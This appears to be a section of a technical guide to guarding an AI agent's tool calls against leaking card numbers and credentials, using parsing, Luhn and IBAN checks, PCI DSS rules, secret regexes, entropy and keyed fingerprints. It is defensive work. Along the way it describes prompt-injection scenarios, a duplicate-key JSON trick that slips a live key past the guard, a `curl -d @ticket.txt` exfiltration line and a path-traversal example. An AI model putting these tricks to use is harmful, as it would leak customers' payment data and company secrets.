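The command sends the contents of Dana's ticket to a website, but neither the card number nor the key appears in the command's text. The guard can strip the quotation marks and scan the literal text. It cannot, in general, work out what a command will output without running it, and the scan has to happen before the command runs.

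Searching for special characters helps only a little. One of ai-tool-guard's examples rejects filenames that contain shell characters such as `$`, `|` and `<`, and the same characters often indicate that a command brings in data from elsewhere. But `curl -d @ticket.txt` sends the file without using any of them. For commands that can reach the network, it is safer to list the few forms that the guard can parse completely and send everything else to review.

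Web addresses are easier to scan. The guard should split the address into its parts before decoding the percent-encoding in each, because an encoded `&` inside a value would otherwise look like the start of a new parameter. It should scan the path, every parameter and any username and password before the host name. It should not open the address, because the request would send out whatever the parameters contain. The guard will therefore miss private material that is only behind a link, as in the screenshot leak that Tom's Hardware reported, where harmless-looking links led to public images containing sensitive information.

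When an argument is a file path, the guard has to find out which file it leads to. Pydantic's example resolves the path before checking that it lies in the permitted folder, because `/workspace/../etc/passwd` starts with that folder's name but leads outside it. If the tool will send the file, the guard should then read its contents. The file could change while the reviewer is deciding, so the runtime should save a copy at the first scan and send that copy.

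Attachments may arrive as base64, as a path or as an identifier in another system. TruffleHog opens more than a dozen compression and archive formats, including zip, and a guard can do the same within its size limit. The guard needs text recognition to scan images and the password to scan an encrypted archive.

| Argument | The guard must resolve | The guard must send to review unread |
|---|---|---|
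| Shell command | Literal text, with quotation marks removed and encodings decoded | Variables, output of other commands, scripts, and files or piped input that it cannot trace |
| URL | Login details, path and every parameter | Whatever lies at the address |
| File path | The real location, and the contents if the tool will send them | Files that are too large or in an unknown format |
| Attachment | Text, common document formats and archives, within the limits | Images without text recognition, encrypted files, files it cannot fetch from another system |

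The guard must report "unread" as a separate result from "clean". Otherwise the reviewer would mistake an encrypted attachment for one the guard had checked. If the tool normally runs without approval, an unread argument should pause the call until someone approves it.

### Why the guard and the tool must use the same parsed object

All of this work is wasted if the tool then reads the arguments differently. Suppose an instruction planted in the ticket leads the model to write the body twice:

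```json
{
  "to": "dana@example.com",
  "body": "The billing key is exk_live_7hQ2mV9xTz4LpR8sWc3NbY6k.",
  "body": "We have fixed the fault. Please try again."
}
```

Python's standard parser keeps the last value, so the guard would scan the harmless sentence, and the reviewer would probably see it too. If the runtime then passed the original string to a mail service whose parser keeps the first value, Dana would receive the key.

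Bishop Fox's *An Exploration of JSON Interoperability Vulnerabilities* demonstrates this flaw in an online shop. Its cart service parsed an order with two quantities for one item, approved the second (1), and forwarded the original text. The payment service used a different parser, read the first quantity (−1), and charged $300 for goods worth $700. The developer had forwarded the original string because it was already at hand and re-serialising the parsed version seemed like wasted effort. Developers may be tempted to forward the original string for the same reasons in an agent runtime that receives its arguments as a string.

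The guard and the tool must therefore use the same parsed object. The runtime parses the arguments once, the guard scans the result, and the function runs with that result. An exact copy also works, provided nothing changes the arguments after the scan. Pydantic, for example, gives its guard a read-only copy.

The JSON standard only recommends that names be unique, and describes the behaviour of software that receives duplicates as unpredictable. *Unexpected security footguns in Go's parsers* (Trail of Bits, 2025) reports that seven of the 49 parsers in Bishop Fox's survey take the first value when a name is repeated. Other differences are more common. *Cross-language fuzzing framework for JSON parsers* (Kivalo and Ginzboorg, 2026) reports exploitable discrepancies in 59.7% of the parser pairs tested. The tests used malformed or ambiguous JSON, so the figure shows what an attacker could exploit,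 but is little evidence of how parsers handle the JSON that models ordinarily produce.

A tool on another company's server has to parse the arguments again, so it can't share a single object with the guard. The runtime should instead serialise the object that the guard scanned and send the result, never the original string. Even this can fail if duplicate keys survive parsing. Bishop Fox found one library that writes both values when it serialises the object, and another that returns the first value when a program looks up the key but writes the second.

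The guard can avoid most of these disagreements by holding any call whose JSON is ambiguous. Bray sets out when software will agree on the contents, which gives the guard three checks:

- **Names are unique within each object.** The comparison should ignore case, because the original JSON parser in the Go language treats `body` and `BODY` as the same field and keeps whichever comes last. Trail of Bits lists version 2 of that parser as fixing this and rejecting duplicates.
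- **Strings contain only valid Unicode.** JSON can express half of a two-part character code, and one Python library that Bishop Fox tested silently drops it. Placed in the middle of a card number, it would break up the digits for the guard and vanish for the recipient.
- **Integers stay within 2^53 − 1 in either direction.** This also catches the long card numbers that some parsers would round.

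The guard has to run these checks while it parses the original string, because an ordinary parser discards the duplicates before it returns an object.

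## Recognising card numbers

Once the arguments are plain strings, the guard must identify which runs of digits are card numbers. Order numbers, phone serial numbers and bank account numbers can be just as long. But card numbers follow an international standard, ISO/IEC 7812, and the guard can use its rules to discard most of the others.

### How a card number is built

A card number has three parts. The first six or eight digits are the issuer prefix, often called the bank identification number (BIN), which identifies the company that issued the card. The next digits, up to 12, identify the customer's account. The last digit is a check digit, which the issuer calculates from all the others.

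The standard allows up to 19 digits, but each card network uses only certain prefixes and lengths. These are the main ones:

| Network | First digits | Number of digits |
|---|---|---|
| Visa | 4 | 13, 16 or 19 |
| Mastercard | 51–55, 2221–2720 | 16 |
| American Express | 34, 37 | 15 |
| Discover | 6011, 644–649, 65 | 16–19 |
| JCB | 3528–3589 | 16–19 |
| UnionPay | 62 | 16–19 |
| Diners Club International | 30, 36, 38, 39 | 14–19 |

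Dana's number, 4111 1111 1111 1111, has 16 digits and starts with 4, so it fits Visa's row. Some national networks use other ranges. For example, Troy cards in Turkey can start with 9792, and Uzcard cards in Uzbekistan can start with 8600.

### The Luhn check

The check digit comes from a formula that Hans Peter Luhn of IBM devised in the 1950s to catch typing errors. To test a number, the detector doubles every second digit from the right, starting with the one before the check digit. If a doubled digit comes to more than 9, the detector subtracts 9. It then adds these results to the remaining digits, including the check digit, and the number passes if the total is a multiple of 10.

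For Dana's card:

```
digit       4 1 1 1   1 1 1 1   1 1 1 1   1 1 1 1
multiplier  2 1 2 1   2 1 2 1   2 1 2 1   2 1 2 1
result      8 1 2 1   2 1 2 1   2 1 2 1   2 1 2 1
subtotal      12    +    6    +    6    +    6     = 30
```

The total is 30, so the number passes. If Dana had typed the third digit as 7, doubling it would give 14, and subtracting 9 would leave 5:

```
digit       4 1 7 1   1 1 1 1   1 1 1 1   1 1 1 1
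multiplier  2 1 2 1   2 1 2 1   2 1 2 1   2 1 2 1
result      8 1 5 1   2 1 2 1   2 1 2 1   2 1 2 1
subtotal      15    +    6    +    6    +    6     = 33
```

The total, 33, is not a multiple of 10, so this number fails. The check catches any single wrong digit. Doubling turns the digits 0 to 9 into ten different values (0, 2, 4, 6, 8, 1, 3, 5, 7 and 9), so a wrong digit always changes the total by 1 to 9. The check also catches swapped neighbouring digits, unless they are 0 and 9.

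A card number with one wrong digit always fails the Luhn check, so a guard that relies on the check will miss it. Someone who sees the mistyped number can still recover the real one. For each of the 16 positions, exactly one replacement digit makes the number pass, so anyone who suspects a single wrong digit has only 16 numbers to try. If a number fails the check but fits a network's range and follows the word "card", the guard should probably report it as a weak finding.

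### False alarms from order numbers

The Luhn check also passes many numbers that aren't card numbers. For any first 15 digits, exactly one of the ten possible last digits passes, so a random 16-digit string has a 10% chance of passing. Requiring the first digit to be from 2 to 6, as it is on the main networks' cards, halves this to 5%.

With a 5% chance of a false match per number, false alarms become likely even in short lists. Suppose the support agent emails a courier 200 order numbers, each with 16 random digits. On average, ten of them will look like card numbers. The chance that none does is 0.95^200, or about 1 in 28,500. Even a list of 14 order numbers is slightly more likely than not to set off the guard.

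Real order numbers are rarely random, which can raise or lower the number of false alarms. If the company's order numbers begin with the date, as in 2026100700000417, they all start with 2, so the first-digit rule removes none of them. About 20 of the 200 would then be false alarms.

**Issuer ranges** help a good deal here. No network in the table uses numbers that start with 2026, so a detector that checks the full prefix would discard all 200. For random order numbers the gain is smaller. The ranges in the table cover about 27% of all 16-digit strings:

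| Test | Random 16-digit strings that pass | Expected false alarms in 200 |
|---|---|---|
| Luhn check | 10% | 20 |
| Luhn check and first digit 2 to 6 | 5% | 10 |
| Luhn check and issuer range | 2.7% | 5 or 6 |

Checking exact lengths matters most for identifiers that also have a Luhn check digit, such as the IMEI, the 15-digit serial number that identifies a phone to mobile networks. Many IMEIs start with 35. These all pass a test for 13 to 19 digits, a first digit from 2 to 6 and a valid check digit, so the guard would flag any tool call in which a phone shop's agent mentioned one. JCB uses some prefixes that start with 35, but only on cards with at least 16 digits, so a detector that checks the lengths allowed for each prefix would not flag these IMEIs.

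The detector should also test only whole runs of digits, meaning those with no other digit directly before or after. If it tries all seven lengths from 13 to 19 starting from one position in a long string of random digits, the chance that at least one passes the Luhn check is 1 − 0.9^7, or about 52%. However, testing only whole runs lets someone hide a card number by attaching an extra digit to it.

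**Nearby words** help rank findings. "Card", "Visa" or "expires" just before a number strengthens the finding, while "order" or "tracking" weakens it. Nearby words shouldn't clear a number completely, because a model acting on a planted instruction could label a real card number as an order reference.

**Known internal formats** can help rule out a number as a card number, provided the guard checks more than the format. If the company's order numbers can be any 16 digits, every 16-digit card number fits that format too. It is better to look the number up in the order system and drop the finding only if that order exists. A company that is free to choose its own format can avoid the problem by putting a letter in the middle of each order number.

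### Two published detectors

Pydantic documents the tests in its `credit_card` pattern, whereas ai-tool-guard's *Guards* says only that `piiGuard` looks for a credit card pattern and applies a Luhn check.

| Rule | Pydantic's `credit_card` | ai-tool-guard's `piiGuard` |
|---|---|---|
| Length | 13 to 19 digits | Not stated |
| First digit | 2 to 6 | Not stated |
| Spacing | Any grouping | Not stated |
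| Check digit | Luhn | Luhn |
| Bank accounts (IBAN) | Separate pattern, runs first | Not among its five types |
| Result of a match | Replaces the number with a placeholder | Rejects the call |

The 5% figure is based on Pydantic's rules, and Pydantic warns in its guide that lists of numbers can lose a value. In the email to the courier, about ten order numbers would turn into `[redacted:credit_card]`, and the courier would have to ask for them. `piiGuard` would reject the whole call on a single match.

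A guard that accepts digits in any grouping can mistake two eight-digit order numbers separated by a space for one card number. Joining list items can cause the same kind of false alarm. The guard could accept unusual groupings but treat them as weaker evidence than the usual four groups of four digits.

Pydantic's first-digit rule also excludes some real cards, including the Troy and Uzcard ranges mentioned above. A company with customers in Turkey or Uzbekistan would need to add those prefixes. Older Maestro debit cards can have as few as 12 digits, so the minimum length excludes them too.

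Before relying on `piiGuard`, a developer should check what its card pattern accepts, either by reading the source code or trying published test numbers of different lengths, with and without spaces. `piiGuard` also looks for email addresses, US Social Security numbers, US phone numbers and IP addresses. An ordinary support email often contains one of these, so a developer who wants to catch only card numbers has to list all four as allowed.

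### Why account numbers should come first

An IBAN (international bank account number) starts with a two-letter country code and two check digits, and people usually write it in groups of four, much like a card number. In the German example DE89 3704 0044 0532 0130 00, a card detector that accepts any grouping could start reading at 3704 and find up to 18 digits beginning with 3. This IBAN fails the Luhn check at every length from 13 to 18, but others will pass by chance.

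Pydantic runs its IBAN pattern before its card pattern for this reason. Developers can choose which patterns to use, but they cannot change the order. The IBAN pattern should also go first because its check is much stronger. To test the German example, the detector does the following:

1. It moves the first four characters to the end, giving 370400440532013000DE89.
2. It replaces each letter with a number, where A is 10, B is 11 and so on. D becomes 13 and E becomes 14, giving 370400440532013000131489.
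3. It divides the result by 97. The IBAN is valid if the remainder is 1, as it is here.

Only about one random string in 97 passes the IBAN check, compared with one in ten for the Luhn check, and an IBAN must also start with a country code. If the card detector ran first and replaced the middle of an IBAN, the rest would no longer match the IBAN pattern, and the reviewer would see a card finding in an email that contained no card number.

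Companies often have good reason to send a bank account number, such as their own on an invoice. But a guard that lets every valid IBAN through would be easy to bypass, because an attacker could put a card number inside a made-up IBAN and calculate matching check digits. Exempting only the company's own accounts is safer.

### What the card industry's rules require

The rules for handling card data are in the PCI Security Standards Council's *Payment Card Industry Data Security Standard* (PCI DSS, 2024), which limits how companies may send, store and display card numbers. Payment networks and the banks that handle merchants' card payments decide which companies have to comply. Version 4.0.1 is current, but the council has begun work on the next one, according to its *Request for Comments PCI Data Security Standard PCI DSS v4.0.1*.

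Under Requirement 4.2.2, a company must use strong encryption for any card number it sends by email, instant messaging, SMS or chat. The PCI Security Standards Council's *Can unencrypted PANs be sent over e-mail, instant messaging, SMS, or chat?* (2025) confirms that this applies to internal messages as well as public networks. It also applies when a customer asks for the number. The agent's email would therefore break the rule even though the card is Dana's own, and so would an approval request that showed the full number in Slack. This messaging rule does not cover a payment tool that has to receive the number to charge the card.

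The standard also covers card numbers that arrive through a channel not meant for them, like the one Dana typed into her ticket. The company can either secure the channel to the full standard or securely delete the number and take steps to stop people sending more. If the scan finds a card number in an outgoing email, the company therefore has good reason to check where the number came from.

### What the guard may store and display

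A company has to make card numbers unreadable wherever it stores them, and the requirement explicitly includes audit and troubleshooting logs. If the guard logs the matched text with each finding, it builds up a file of card numbers. The same problem arises if the runtime saves a held tool call to disk while it waits for approval.

The standard accepts four methods for making a stored number unreadable: encryption, truncation (permanently deleting part of the number), index tokens that stand in for the number, and one-way hashes of the whole number. A hash is a fixed-length code that software computes from a value and cannot directly reverse. Hashes help the guard compare the scans before and after review, because it can recognise a number the reviewer has already seen without storing the number itself.

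An ordinary hash is not enough to hide a card number in a log. If the log also shows the first six and last four digits of a 16-digit number, only six digits are missing. That leaves a million possibilities, of which 100,000 pass the Luhn check, and a computer can hash all of those almost instantly to find the match. PCI DSS has therefore required keyed hashes, which also depend on a secret key, since 31 March 2025.

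Most staff may see at most the BIN and the last four digits of a card number on screens and in printouts. According to the PCI Security Standards Council's *How can an entity meet PCI DSS requirements for PAN masking*, anyone who sees more needs a business reason that the company has documented and management has approved. The standard also advises showing only the digits that a task needs. Dana only needs to know which of her cards failed, so "your card ending in 1111" is enough.

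### Security codes

The security code is the three- or four-digit number printed on a card, which shops use to verify online and telephone payments. Someone with both the code and the card number can make such payments fraudulently. PCI DSS therefore has stricter rules for the code than for the card number. Once the bank has approved or declined a payment, the company may not store the code, even if the code is encrypted or the company does not hold the card number. Only card issuers and companies that support them are exempt.

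A guard should rate a card number with a security code as more serious than a card number alone. The expiry date adds to the risk, since many online shops ask for all three. If the code came from an old ticket, the company has probably already broken the rule against storing security codes, whether or not the email is sent.

Security codes have no check digit, and reporting every three-digit number would produce too many false alarms to be useful. A detector can instead look for three or four digits after a label such as "CVV", "CVC" or "security code", or for a standalone three- or four-digit number near a card number or expiry date. It should report a labelled code even when the call contains no card number, because an earlier message may already have given the recipient the other card details.

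The standard groups magnetic stripe contents with security codes. One of the stripe's tracks has the card number between a semicolon and an equals sign, and the expiry date directly after the equals sign. A card match followed by an equals sign and more digits should therefore get the same high rating as a security code.

### Truncated numbers and payment tokens

A truncated card number is normally safe to let through. The PCI Security Standards Council's *What are acceptable formats for truncation of primary account numbers?* gives the usual limit as the first six and last four digits. For 16-digit cards with an eight-digit BIN, the networks listed in SecureTrust's *Migration to Eight Digit Bank Identification Numbers* allow the first eight digits and any other four. A correctly truncated number therefore has at most 12 digits, so a detector that requires at least 13 will never report one.

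Two different truncations of the same card number can together reveal much more than either does alone. For a 16-digit card with a six-digit BIN, SecureTrust gives the limit as the first six digits and any other four. One system might keep the first six and last four digits, while another keeps the first ten. Anyone with both versions lacks only two digits, and only ten of the 100 possible pairs pass the Luhn check. If the guard truncates card numbers, it should therefore use the same format everywhere, and keeping only the last four digits is safest.

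A guard that truncates card numbers falls within the scope of PCI DSS, as do the systems connected to it, according to the PCI Security Standards Council's *Are truncated Primary Account Numbers (PAN) required to be protected*. Systems that only ever handle truncated numbers can fall outside that scope if the company separates them properly from its card systems.

A company can store payment tokens in place of card numbers. Many are strings of letters and digits that a card detector will ignore. Others keep the BIN and the last four digits and replace only the middle, so that older payment software still accepts them. These have the length and prefix of a real card number, and some will pass the Luhn check. The council leaves assessors to decide, case by case, whether such tokens fall under the standard.

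The guard cannot tell this kind of token from a card number by its digits, so it should treat it as a card number unless the token system confirms that it is a token. A company that controls its own token system may be able to configure it to issue only tokens that fail the Luhn check.

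## Recognising keys, tokens and passwords

Card numbers follow one international standard, but every company that issues credentials can design its own format. Some make their keys easy to recognise, while others issue strings that are effectively random, and people choose passwords like "bluebird77". No single method finds all of these, so a guard needs several. It should record which method produced each finding, because some methods give much stronger evidence than others.

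### Fixed formats

Many issuers start their keys with a fixed prefix, partly so that software can spot a leaked one. Checking the prefix along with the length and the permitted characters makes a chance match very unlikely.

| Credential | Form |
|---|---|
| AWS access key ID | `AKIA`, then 16 capital letters or digits |
| GitHub personal access token (classic) | `ghp_`, then 36 letters or digits |
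| Google Cloud API key | `AIza`, then 35 characters |
| SendGrid API key | `SG.`, then 22 characters, a dot and 43 characters |
| JSON Web Token | Three parts separated by dots, starting with `eyJ` |
| Private key | A block whose first line contains `BEGIN` and `PRIVATE KEY` |
| The billing key in Dana's email | `exk_live_`, then 24 letters or digits |

No ready-made list will contain the pattern in the last row, because the billing service is invented, and none will cover keys that a company issues itself. Pydantic's secret detector accepts extra patterns, so a developer can add `exk_live_[A-Za-z0-9]{24}` in one line. ai-tool-guard has built-in patterns for AWS keys, GitHub tokens, JSON Web Tokens and private keys, but they are in a filter that runs on a tool's result. To check the arguments, the developer has to write the patterns again in one of the library's argument guards.

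Some formats allow a second check, much like the Luhn check for card numbers. The last six characters of a GitHub token are a 32-bit checksum, and a random string has about a one in four billion chance of matching it.

A JSON Web Token (JWT) is a signed statement, often about who is logged in. Its first two parts, a header and the contents, are JSON encoded in base64url, a variant of base64 that is safe in web addresses. Both parts usually start with `eyJ`, which is how the usual opening of a JSON object, `{"`, is encoded. A detector doesn't need the signing key to decode the header, check that it names a signing method, and read the expiry time from the contents. An expired token is a much less serious finding.

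Private keys are easy to find, but a pattern that matches only the opening line will redact that line and leave the key itself in the email. Pydantic's pattern matches the whole block, even if someone pasted it without its closing line.

### The character after the key

A rule for detecting a key usually limits which characters can follow it, so that the rule doesn't match part of a longer string. This limit causes many misses. Mishra (2026), in *Boundary-Mutation Testing for Pattern-Based Secret Detection*, generated fake credentials from scanners' own rules and placed them in different contexts, such as a quoted value, a list and a web address.

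Version 8.21.2 of Gitleaks found AWS, Google Cloud, npm, Stripe and SendGrid keys and JWTs when a quotation mark, space or semicolon followed them. It missed all of them before a comma, closing bracket, ampersand or question mark, because its rules allow only a short list of next characters. The full stop isn't on that list either, so a rule copied from this version and adapted to `exk_live_` would presumably miss the billing key in Dana's email, which comes at the end of a sentence.

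Parsing the arguments first, as described earlier, avoids part of this problem. A key that fills a whole field has nothing after it, and a guard that splits web addresses into parameters removes the ampersand. Parsing doesn't help with keys in running text.

Mishra's own scanner had a different fault. Five of its rules ended in `\b`, which matches only where a letter, digit or underscore meets another kind of character. The rule fails when a key ends in a hyphen and a space follows, because neither is a letter, digit or underscore. SendGrid keys use 64 characters, including the hyphen, so if the last character is random, the scanner misses one key in 64.

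This fault doesn't affect JWTs signed with the common HS256 method, because their signatures can't end in a hyphen. The signature has 256 bits and each base64url character carries 6, so the first 42 characters carry 252 bits and the last one carries only 4. The encoder fills the last character's other two bits with zeros, so its position in the base64url alphabet, counting from 0, must be a multiple of 4. This rules out the hyphen, which is at position 62.

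Rules for keys of variable length failed less obviously, often matching the key without its final hyphen. Such a match is enough to raise an alarm, but it gives the guard the wrong value to redact or compare. Mishra recommends replacing the final `\b` with `(?![A-Za-z0-9_])`, which only forbids a letter, digit or underscore from coming next. An earlier repair also forbade a hyphen, which made two rules miss keys they had previously found.

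### A name beside the value

An AWS secret access key is forty base64 characters with no prefix. (It works together with the access key ID, which starts with `AKIA` and is not secret on its own.) A pattern for its shape alone would match a lot of ordinary base64, and also every standard Git commit identifier, which is forty hexadecimal digits. Pydantic therefore leaves this key out of its defaults and advises developers to look for the name next to it:

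```
aws_secret_access_key\s*[=:]\s*["']?([A-Za-z0-9/+]{40})(?![A-Za-z0-9/+=])
```

In a tool call, a credential's name is often a JSON field name. After the guard has walked the arguments, `aws_secret_access_key` and its value are two separate strings, so a pattern that needs them together matches neither. The guard can fix this by also scanning a `name=value` string for every field.

The same method covers database passwords in connection strings, command-line options such as `--password`, and labels such as "Authorization: Bearer". It misses a secret if the model introduces it with words that the pattern doesn't include, such as "Here is what you need to get into our AWS account" instead of the key's official name.

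Adding more words brings false alarms, especially in customer support, where passwords are an everyday subject. A guard should not block an email that says "Your password must contain twelve characters." On real code, six of the ten false alarms from Mishra's scanner came from one line of documentation, a database address with the words "username" and "password" in place of real credentials. A guard can ignore obvious placeholders like these, but not `$DB_PASSWORD` in a shell command, because the shell will replace it with the real password.

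An AWS access key ID can replace the name as evidence that another string in the call is a secret key. In Mishra's tests, TruffleHog reported none of the AWS credentials when the ID appeared alone and all of them when the secret key accompanied it. A guard that finds an `AKIA` string could therefore treat any forty-character base64 string in the same call as a probable secret key, even in another field.

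### Randomness

Where there is neither a format nor a name, a scanner can measure how random a string looks. The usual measure is Shannon entropy:

```
H = − Σ p(c) × log2 p(c)
```

Here p(c) is the fraction of the string's characters that are c, and the sum runs over each distinct character in the string. The result is in bits per character.

In the word "password", the letter s makes up 2/8 of the characters, and six other letters make up 1/8 each:

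```
H = 2/8 × log2(4) + 6 × 1/8 × log2(8)
  = 0.5 + 2.25
  = 2.75
```

The random part of the billing key, `7hQ2mV9xTz4LpR8sWc3NbY6k`, has 24 characters, all different:

```
H = 24 × 1/24 × log2(24) = 4.58
```

A threshold of 4 bits would separate these two, but it fails on many other strings.

| String | Length | Bits per character | Secret? |
|---|---|---|---|
| A random password with no repeated character | 8 | 3.00 | Yes |
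| `subscription` | 12 | 3.25 | No |
| A Git commit identifier | 40 | About 3.7 | No |
| A random hexadecimal API key | 40 | About 3.7 | Yes |
| `abcdefghijklmnopqrstuvwx` | 24 | 4.58 | No |
| `7hQ2mV9xTz4LpR8sWc3NbY6k` | 24 | 4.58 | Yes |

A string of n characters can have a Shannon entropy of at most log2(n) bits per character, so an eight-character password never scores above 3, however random it is. Scanners therefore apply the entropy test only to longer strings (20 characters or more in Mishra's scanner) and miss most passwords.

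Hexadecimal text uses only 16 different characters, so its Shannon entropy can't exceed 4 bits per character. A threshold of 4 therefore misses all hexadecimal keys, while a threshold of 3.5 flags them but also flags most commit identifiers and file hashes. No entropy threshold can separate keys from hashes, because a random hexadecimal key and a hash of the same length have the same character statistics.

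The formula also ignores the order of the characters, which is why the start of the alphabet scores the same as the key. One of the false alarms in Mishra's test, for example, was a constant that lists the characters allowed unescaped in web addresses.

Emails from a support agent contain many random strings, such as tracking codes, message identifiers and unsubscribe links. A password-reset link contains a real credential, but the customer is supposed to receive it. Entropy is therefore more useful as support for another clue than on its own. For example, if a string follows "the password is", high entropy strengthens the finding.

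### Comparison with the company's own secrets

A company can check whether a string is one of its own secrets by comparing it with the secrets in its vault. A match on a long random value is almost never a coincidence, and the method works even for secrets with no recognisable shape. The reviewer also learns exactly which secret the agent was about to send, which in Dana's case was the live key to the billing service.

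A list of all the secrets, given to the guard so it can recognise them, would be more valuable to a thief than anything the guard protects. The list could be exposed because the guard handles text that attackers can influence, writes logs and crash reports, and may run on the same machine as the agent. In the NordLayer case, a coding assistant collected every environment variable it could reach, and it could have picked up a list of secrets just as easily.

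The guard should hold keyed fingerprints instead. These are the keyed hashes that PCI DSS requires for card numbers, often computed with HMAC. The vault computes a fingerprint of each secret, and the guard fingerprints the text the same way and looks for matches.

A hash of a whole email has nothing in common with the hash of a key inside it, so the guard has to compare pieces. It can slide a window of fixed length along the text:

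```python
WINDOW = 12

def fingerprints(text):
    return {hmac_sha256(FINGERPRINT_KEY, text[i:i + WINDOW])
            for i in range(len(text) - WINDOW + 1)}

# In the vault, once for each secret, without the public prefix
known = fingerprints("7hQ2mV9xTz4LpR8sWc3NbY6k")    # 13 fingerprints

# In the guard, for each string in the arguments
found = known & fingerprints(body)
```

With 12-character windows, an email of 2,000 characters needs 1,989 fingerprints, which take a few milliseconds to calculate. Checking each window also catches a key that the model has cut short or attached to another word, as long as 12 characters in a row survive. The vault leaves out the prefix `exk_live_` because every key from that service starts with it.

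Shorter windows catch smaller fragments but make a secret easier to recover from a stolen list of fingerprints. A thief who also has the fingerprint key and can test ten billion guesses per second would need about 10,000 years to try every combination of 12 letters and digits. With six-character windows, this would take about six seconds, and each further character would then need at most 62 guesses because the windows overlap.

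Passwords people choose are even weaker, because a thief can try common ones first. It is safer to keep the fingerprint key in a small internal service that receives the text and returns only the matches.

Passwords made of ordinary words also cause false alarms. If an administrator's password is "subscription-renewal", one of its 12-character windows is "subscription", and the guard would stop every email containing that word. For such passwords, the guard should compare only the whole value. If the whole password is a common word, the company should change it, because even comparing the whole value will cause false alarms.

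This method misses every secret that isn't in the vault, such as a customer's password, another company's key, or a key that an engineer has just created and pasted into a ticket. The vault also has to update the fingerprints whenever someone replaces a secret.

### Passwords in ordinary sentences

The sentence "log in as Dana and use bluebird77, same as last time" contains a password with no fixed format, no label and little randomness. A language model can identify "bluebird77" as a password from context, and this may be the only method that works for text like this.

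The published results are encouraging, but they come from an easier task than scanning an agent's tool calls. They measure precision, the share of a scanner's findings that are real secrets, and recall, the share of real secrets that it finds. F1 combines the two into one score. *Secret Breach Detection in Source Code with Large Language Models* (2025) reports an F1 of 0.985 for LLaMA-3.1 8B, a fairly small model, after further training for this task. The test set contained 1,500 secrets and 1,500 harmless strings.

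All 3,000 came from a pattern search, so the test shows that a model can sort through what patterns have already found, but not how many passwords it would find in prose that no pattern matches.

The even split also makes the result look better than it would be in use. If the model's errors were evenly divided between missed secrets and false alarms, it would flag about 1.5% of the harmless strings. If only one in 1,000 suspicious strings in a company's tool calls were a real secret, the model would raise about 15 false alarms for each secret it found, a precision of about 6%.

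A model that reads the arguments is also open to prompt injection. An attacker who can make the agent send a key may be able to add a sentence saying that the key is a harmless example. The model should therefore be able to add findings, but not cancel those from a fixed format or an exact match. Like the pattern matching, the model should run on the company's own machines.

### How well published scanners do

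Mishra tested Gitleaks, TruffleHog and her own scanner, GitHub Autopilot, on 400 generated credentials of ten types and 700 harmless lines. She did not test GitHub's hosted secret scanning, which belongs to the same family of tools. *Secrets That Survive Everything* (2026) used 194 credentials exposed in live web applications.

| Test | Scanner | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|---|
| Generated credentials (Mishra) | GitHub Autopilot | 96% | 100% |
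| Generated credentials (Mishra) | Gitleaks | 100% | 80–90% |
| Generated credentials (Mishra) | TruffleHog | 100% | 60% |
| Live web applications (*Secrets That Survive Everything*) | Titus | 78.4% | 20.6% |

The recall figures in Mishra's test do not support a ranking of the scanners. Each scanner found either all 40 examples of a credential type or none, so the test compares them on ten types rather than 400 credentials. Autopilot found four types that TruffleHog missed, and TruffleHog found none that Autopilot missed. If the two were equally good, a split this uneven would occur by chance one time in eight. Gitleaks's recall is given as a range because it rose once the generated JWTs had a proper internal structure.

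TruffleHog's detection rate also depends on whether the file contains other credentials. In a related test on the types it supports, it found 67% of credentials that stood alone and 100% of those that appeared together.

The number of false alarms varies even more with the material scanned. *Argus* (2025) counted 370 from TruffleHog and 635 from Gitleaks in ten popular GitHub repositories. In three outside projects that Mishra scanned, TruffleHog produced more than Gitleaks, 27 to 12. On the live web applications, the scanner SecretFinder produced 1,402 false alarms.

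*Secrets That Survive Everything* rates SecretSifter, a scanner for web traffic, above the other tools it measured that do not use a language model. Web traffic is probably closer to tool calls than source code is. But *SecretSifter* (2026), an evaluation by the tool's own developer, covers only one organisation's applications. A language model also helped compile the list of real secrets, so a scanner would not be penalised for missing any that both the model and a human analyst overlooked.

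These results only partly apply to tool arguments. The formats are the same, so a scanner that has no rule for a type of key in code will not find it in an email either. But an email usually contains only one credential, and TruffleHog performed worst when there was only one. Keys in prose are also followed by full stops and commas, which Gitleaks' rules handle badly. False alarms have different sources too, such as order numbers and tracking links instead of sample passwords in documentation. A company can therefore use the published figures to choose its initial rules, but not to predict how many leaks its guard will miss.

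### Why a guard should not test keys online

Some scanners reduce false alarms by testing whether a suspected key works. TruffleHog can send the key to the service that issued it and see whether the service accepts it. Mishra had to turn this check off because her test environment had no network access. The check is useful for searching old code because it separates the live keys from the thousands of expired ones.

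A guard that tests whether a secret works would send it to an outside party while the call was still waiting for approval. If the format is ambiguous, the guard might send one company's key to several others. Connection strings are riskier because they contain the address the guard would contact. An attacker could get the agent to write the database password into a string that points to the attacker's own server, and the guard would send the password there when it tested the string.

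A failed test also doesn't prove that a key is invalid, because the service may accept it only from certain addresses or may be temporarily down. Using a customer's credential could amount to unauthorised access. The checksum, the expiry time in a JWT and the comparison with the vault give much of the same information without sending the secret outside the company. If the company still needs to know whether one of its own keys works, its security team can test it later with the right issuer.

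### Canary credentials

A canary credential is a planted decoy that nobody has a legitimate reason to use, so any attempt to use it reveals a leak. AWS keys work well as canaries because they can be real keys to an empty account, and AWS records every attempt to use them.

The largest published use of canaries with AI services comes from Dragos, a company that secures industrial systems. In *Three breaches, endless leaks*, its chief research officer, Moore (2026), investigated what happens to prompts after they leave the customer. Between July and November 2026, his team sent nearly two million prompts to widely used AI services, with unique web links and credentials planted in them. UA.News' *Study finds secret leaks in AI service chains* reports that each secret went into only one request to one provider, so when someone used a secret, the team could tell which request had leaked and which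 provider had received it.

Constantin (2026) reports in *Dragos planted 2m secrets in AI prompts and caught 3 hacked providers* that Dragos found signs of break-ins at three companies that host AI models. The earliest dated from mid-July, and none of the companies knew until Dragos told them. In the largest break-in, attackers copied every request that Dragos sent during a few short periods in late October, including a couple of hundred AWS keys. They tried some of the keys within hours, searched for more credentials and attempted to create their own users. The planted keys appeared in tens of thousands of calls to AWS. Moore concludes that the attackers were copying data where requests came in, because the provider had rejected some of the stolen requests before any model ran.

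Other leaks did not require a break-in. Some companies resell access to models through online marketplaces, and Cybernews' *AI routers are leaking your passwords. Here's the proof* reports that several resellers could read and keep customers' prompts with ordinary logging. Moore's team traced the leaks by sending identical requests through different resellers and watching which secrets were used.

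Systems at a Chinese AI lab also opened the planted links from more than half of the requests sent to its models between July and October. They opened links from about two-thirds of the requests marked "no data collection" or Zero Data Retention, which means the provider should not routinely store prompts.

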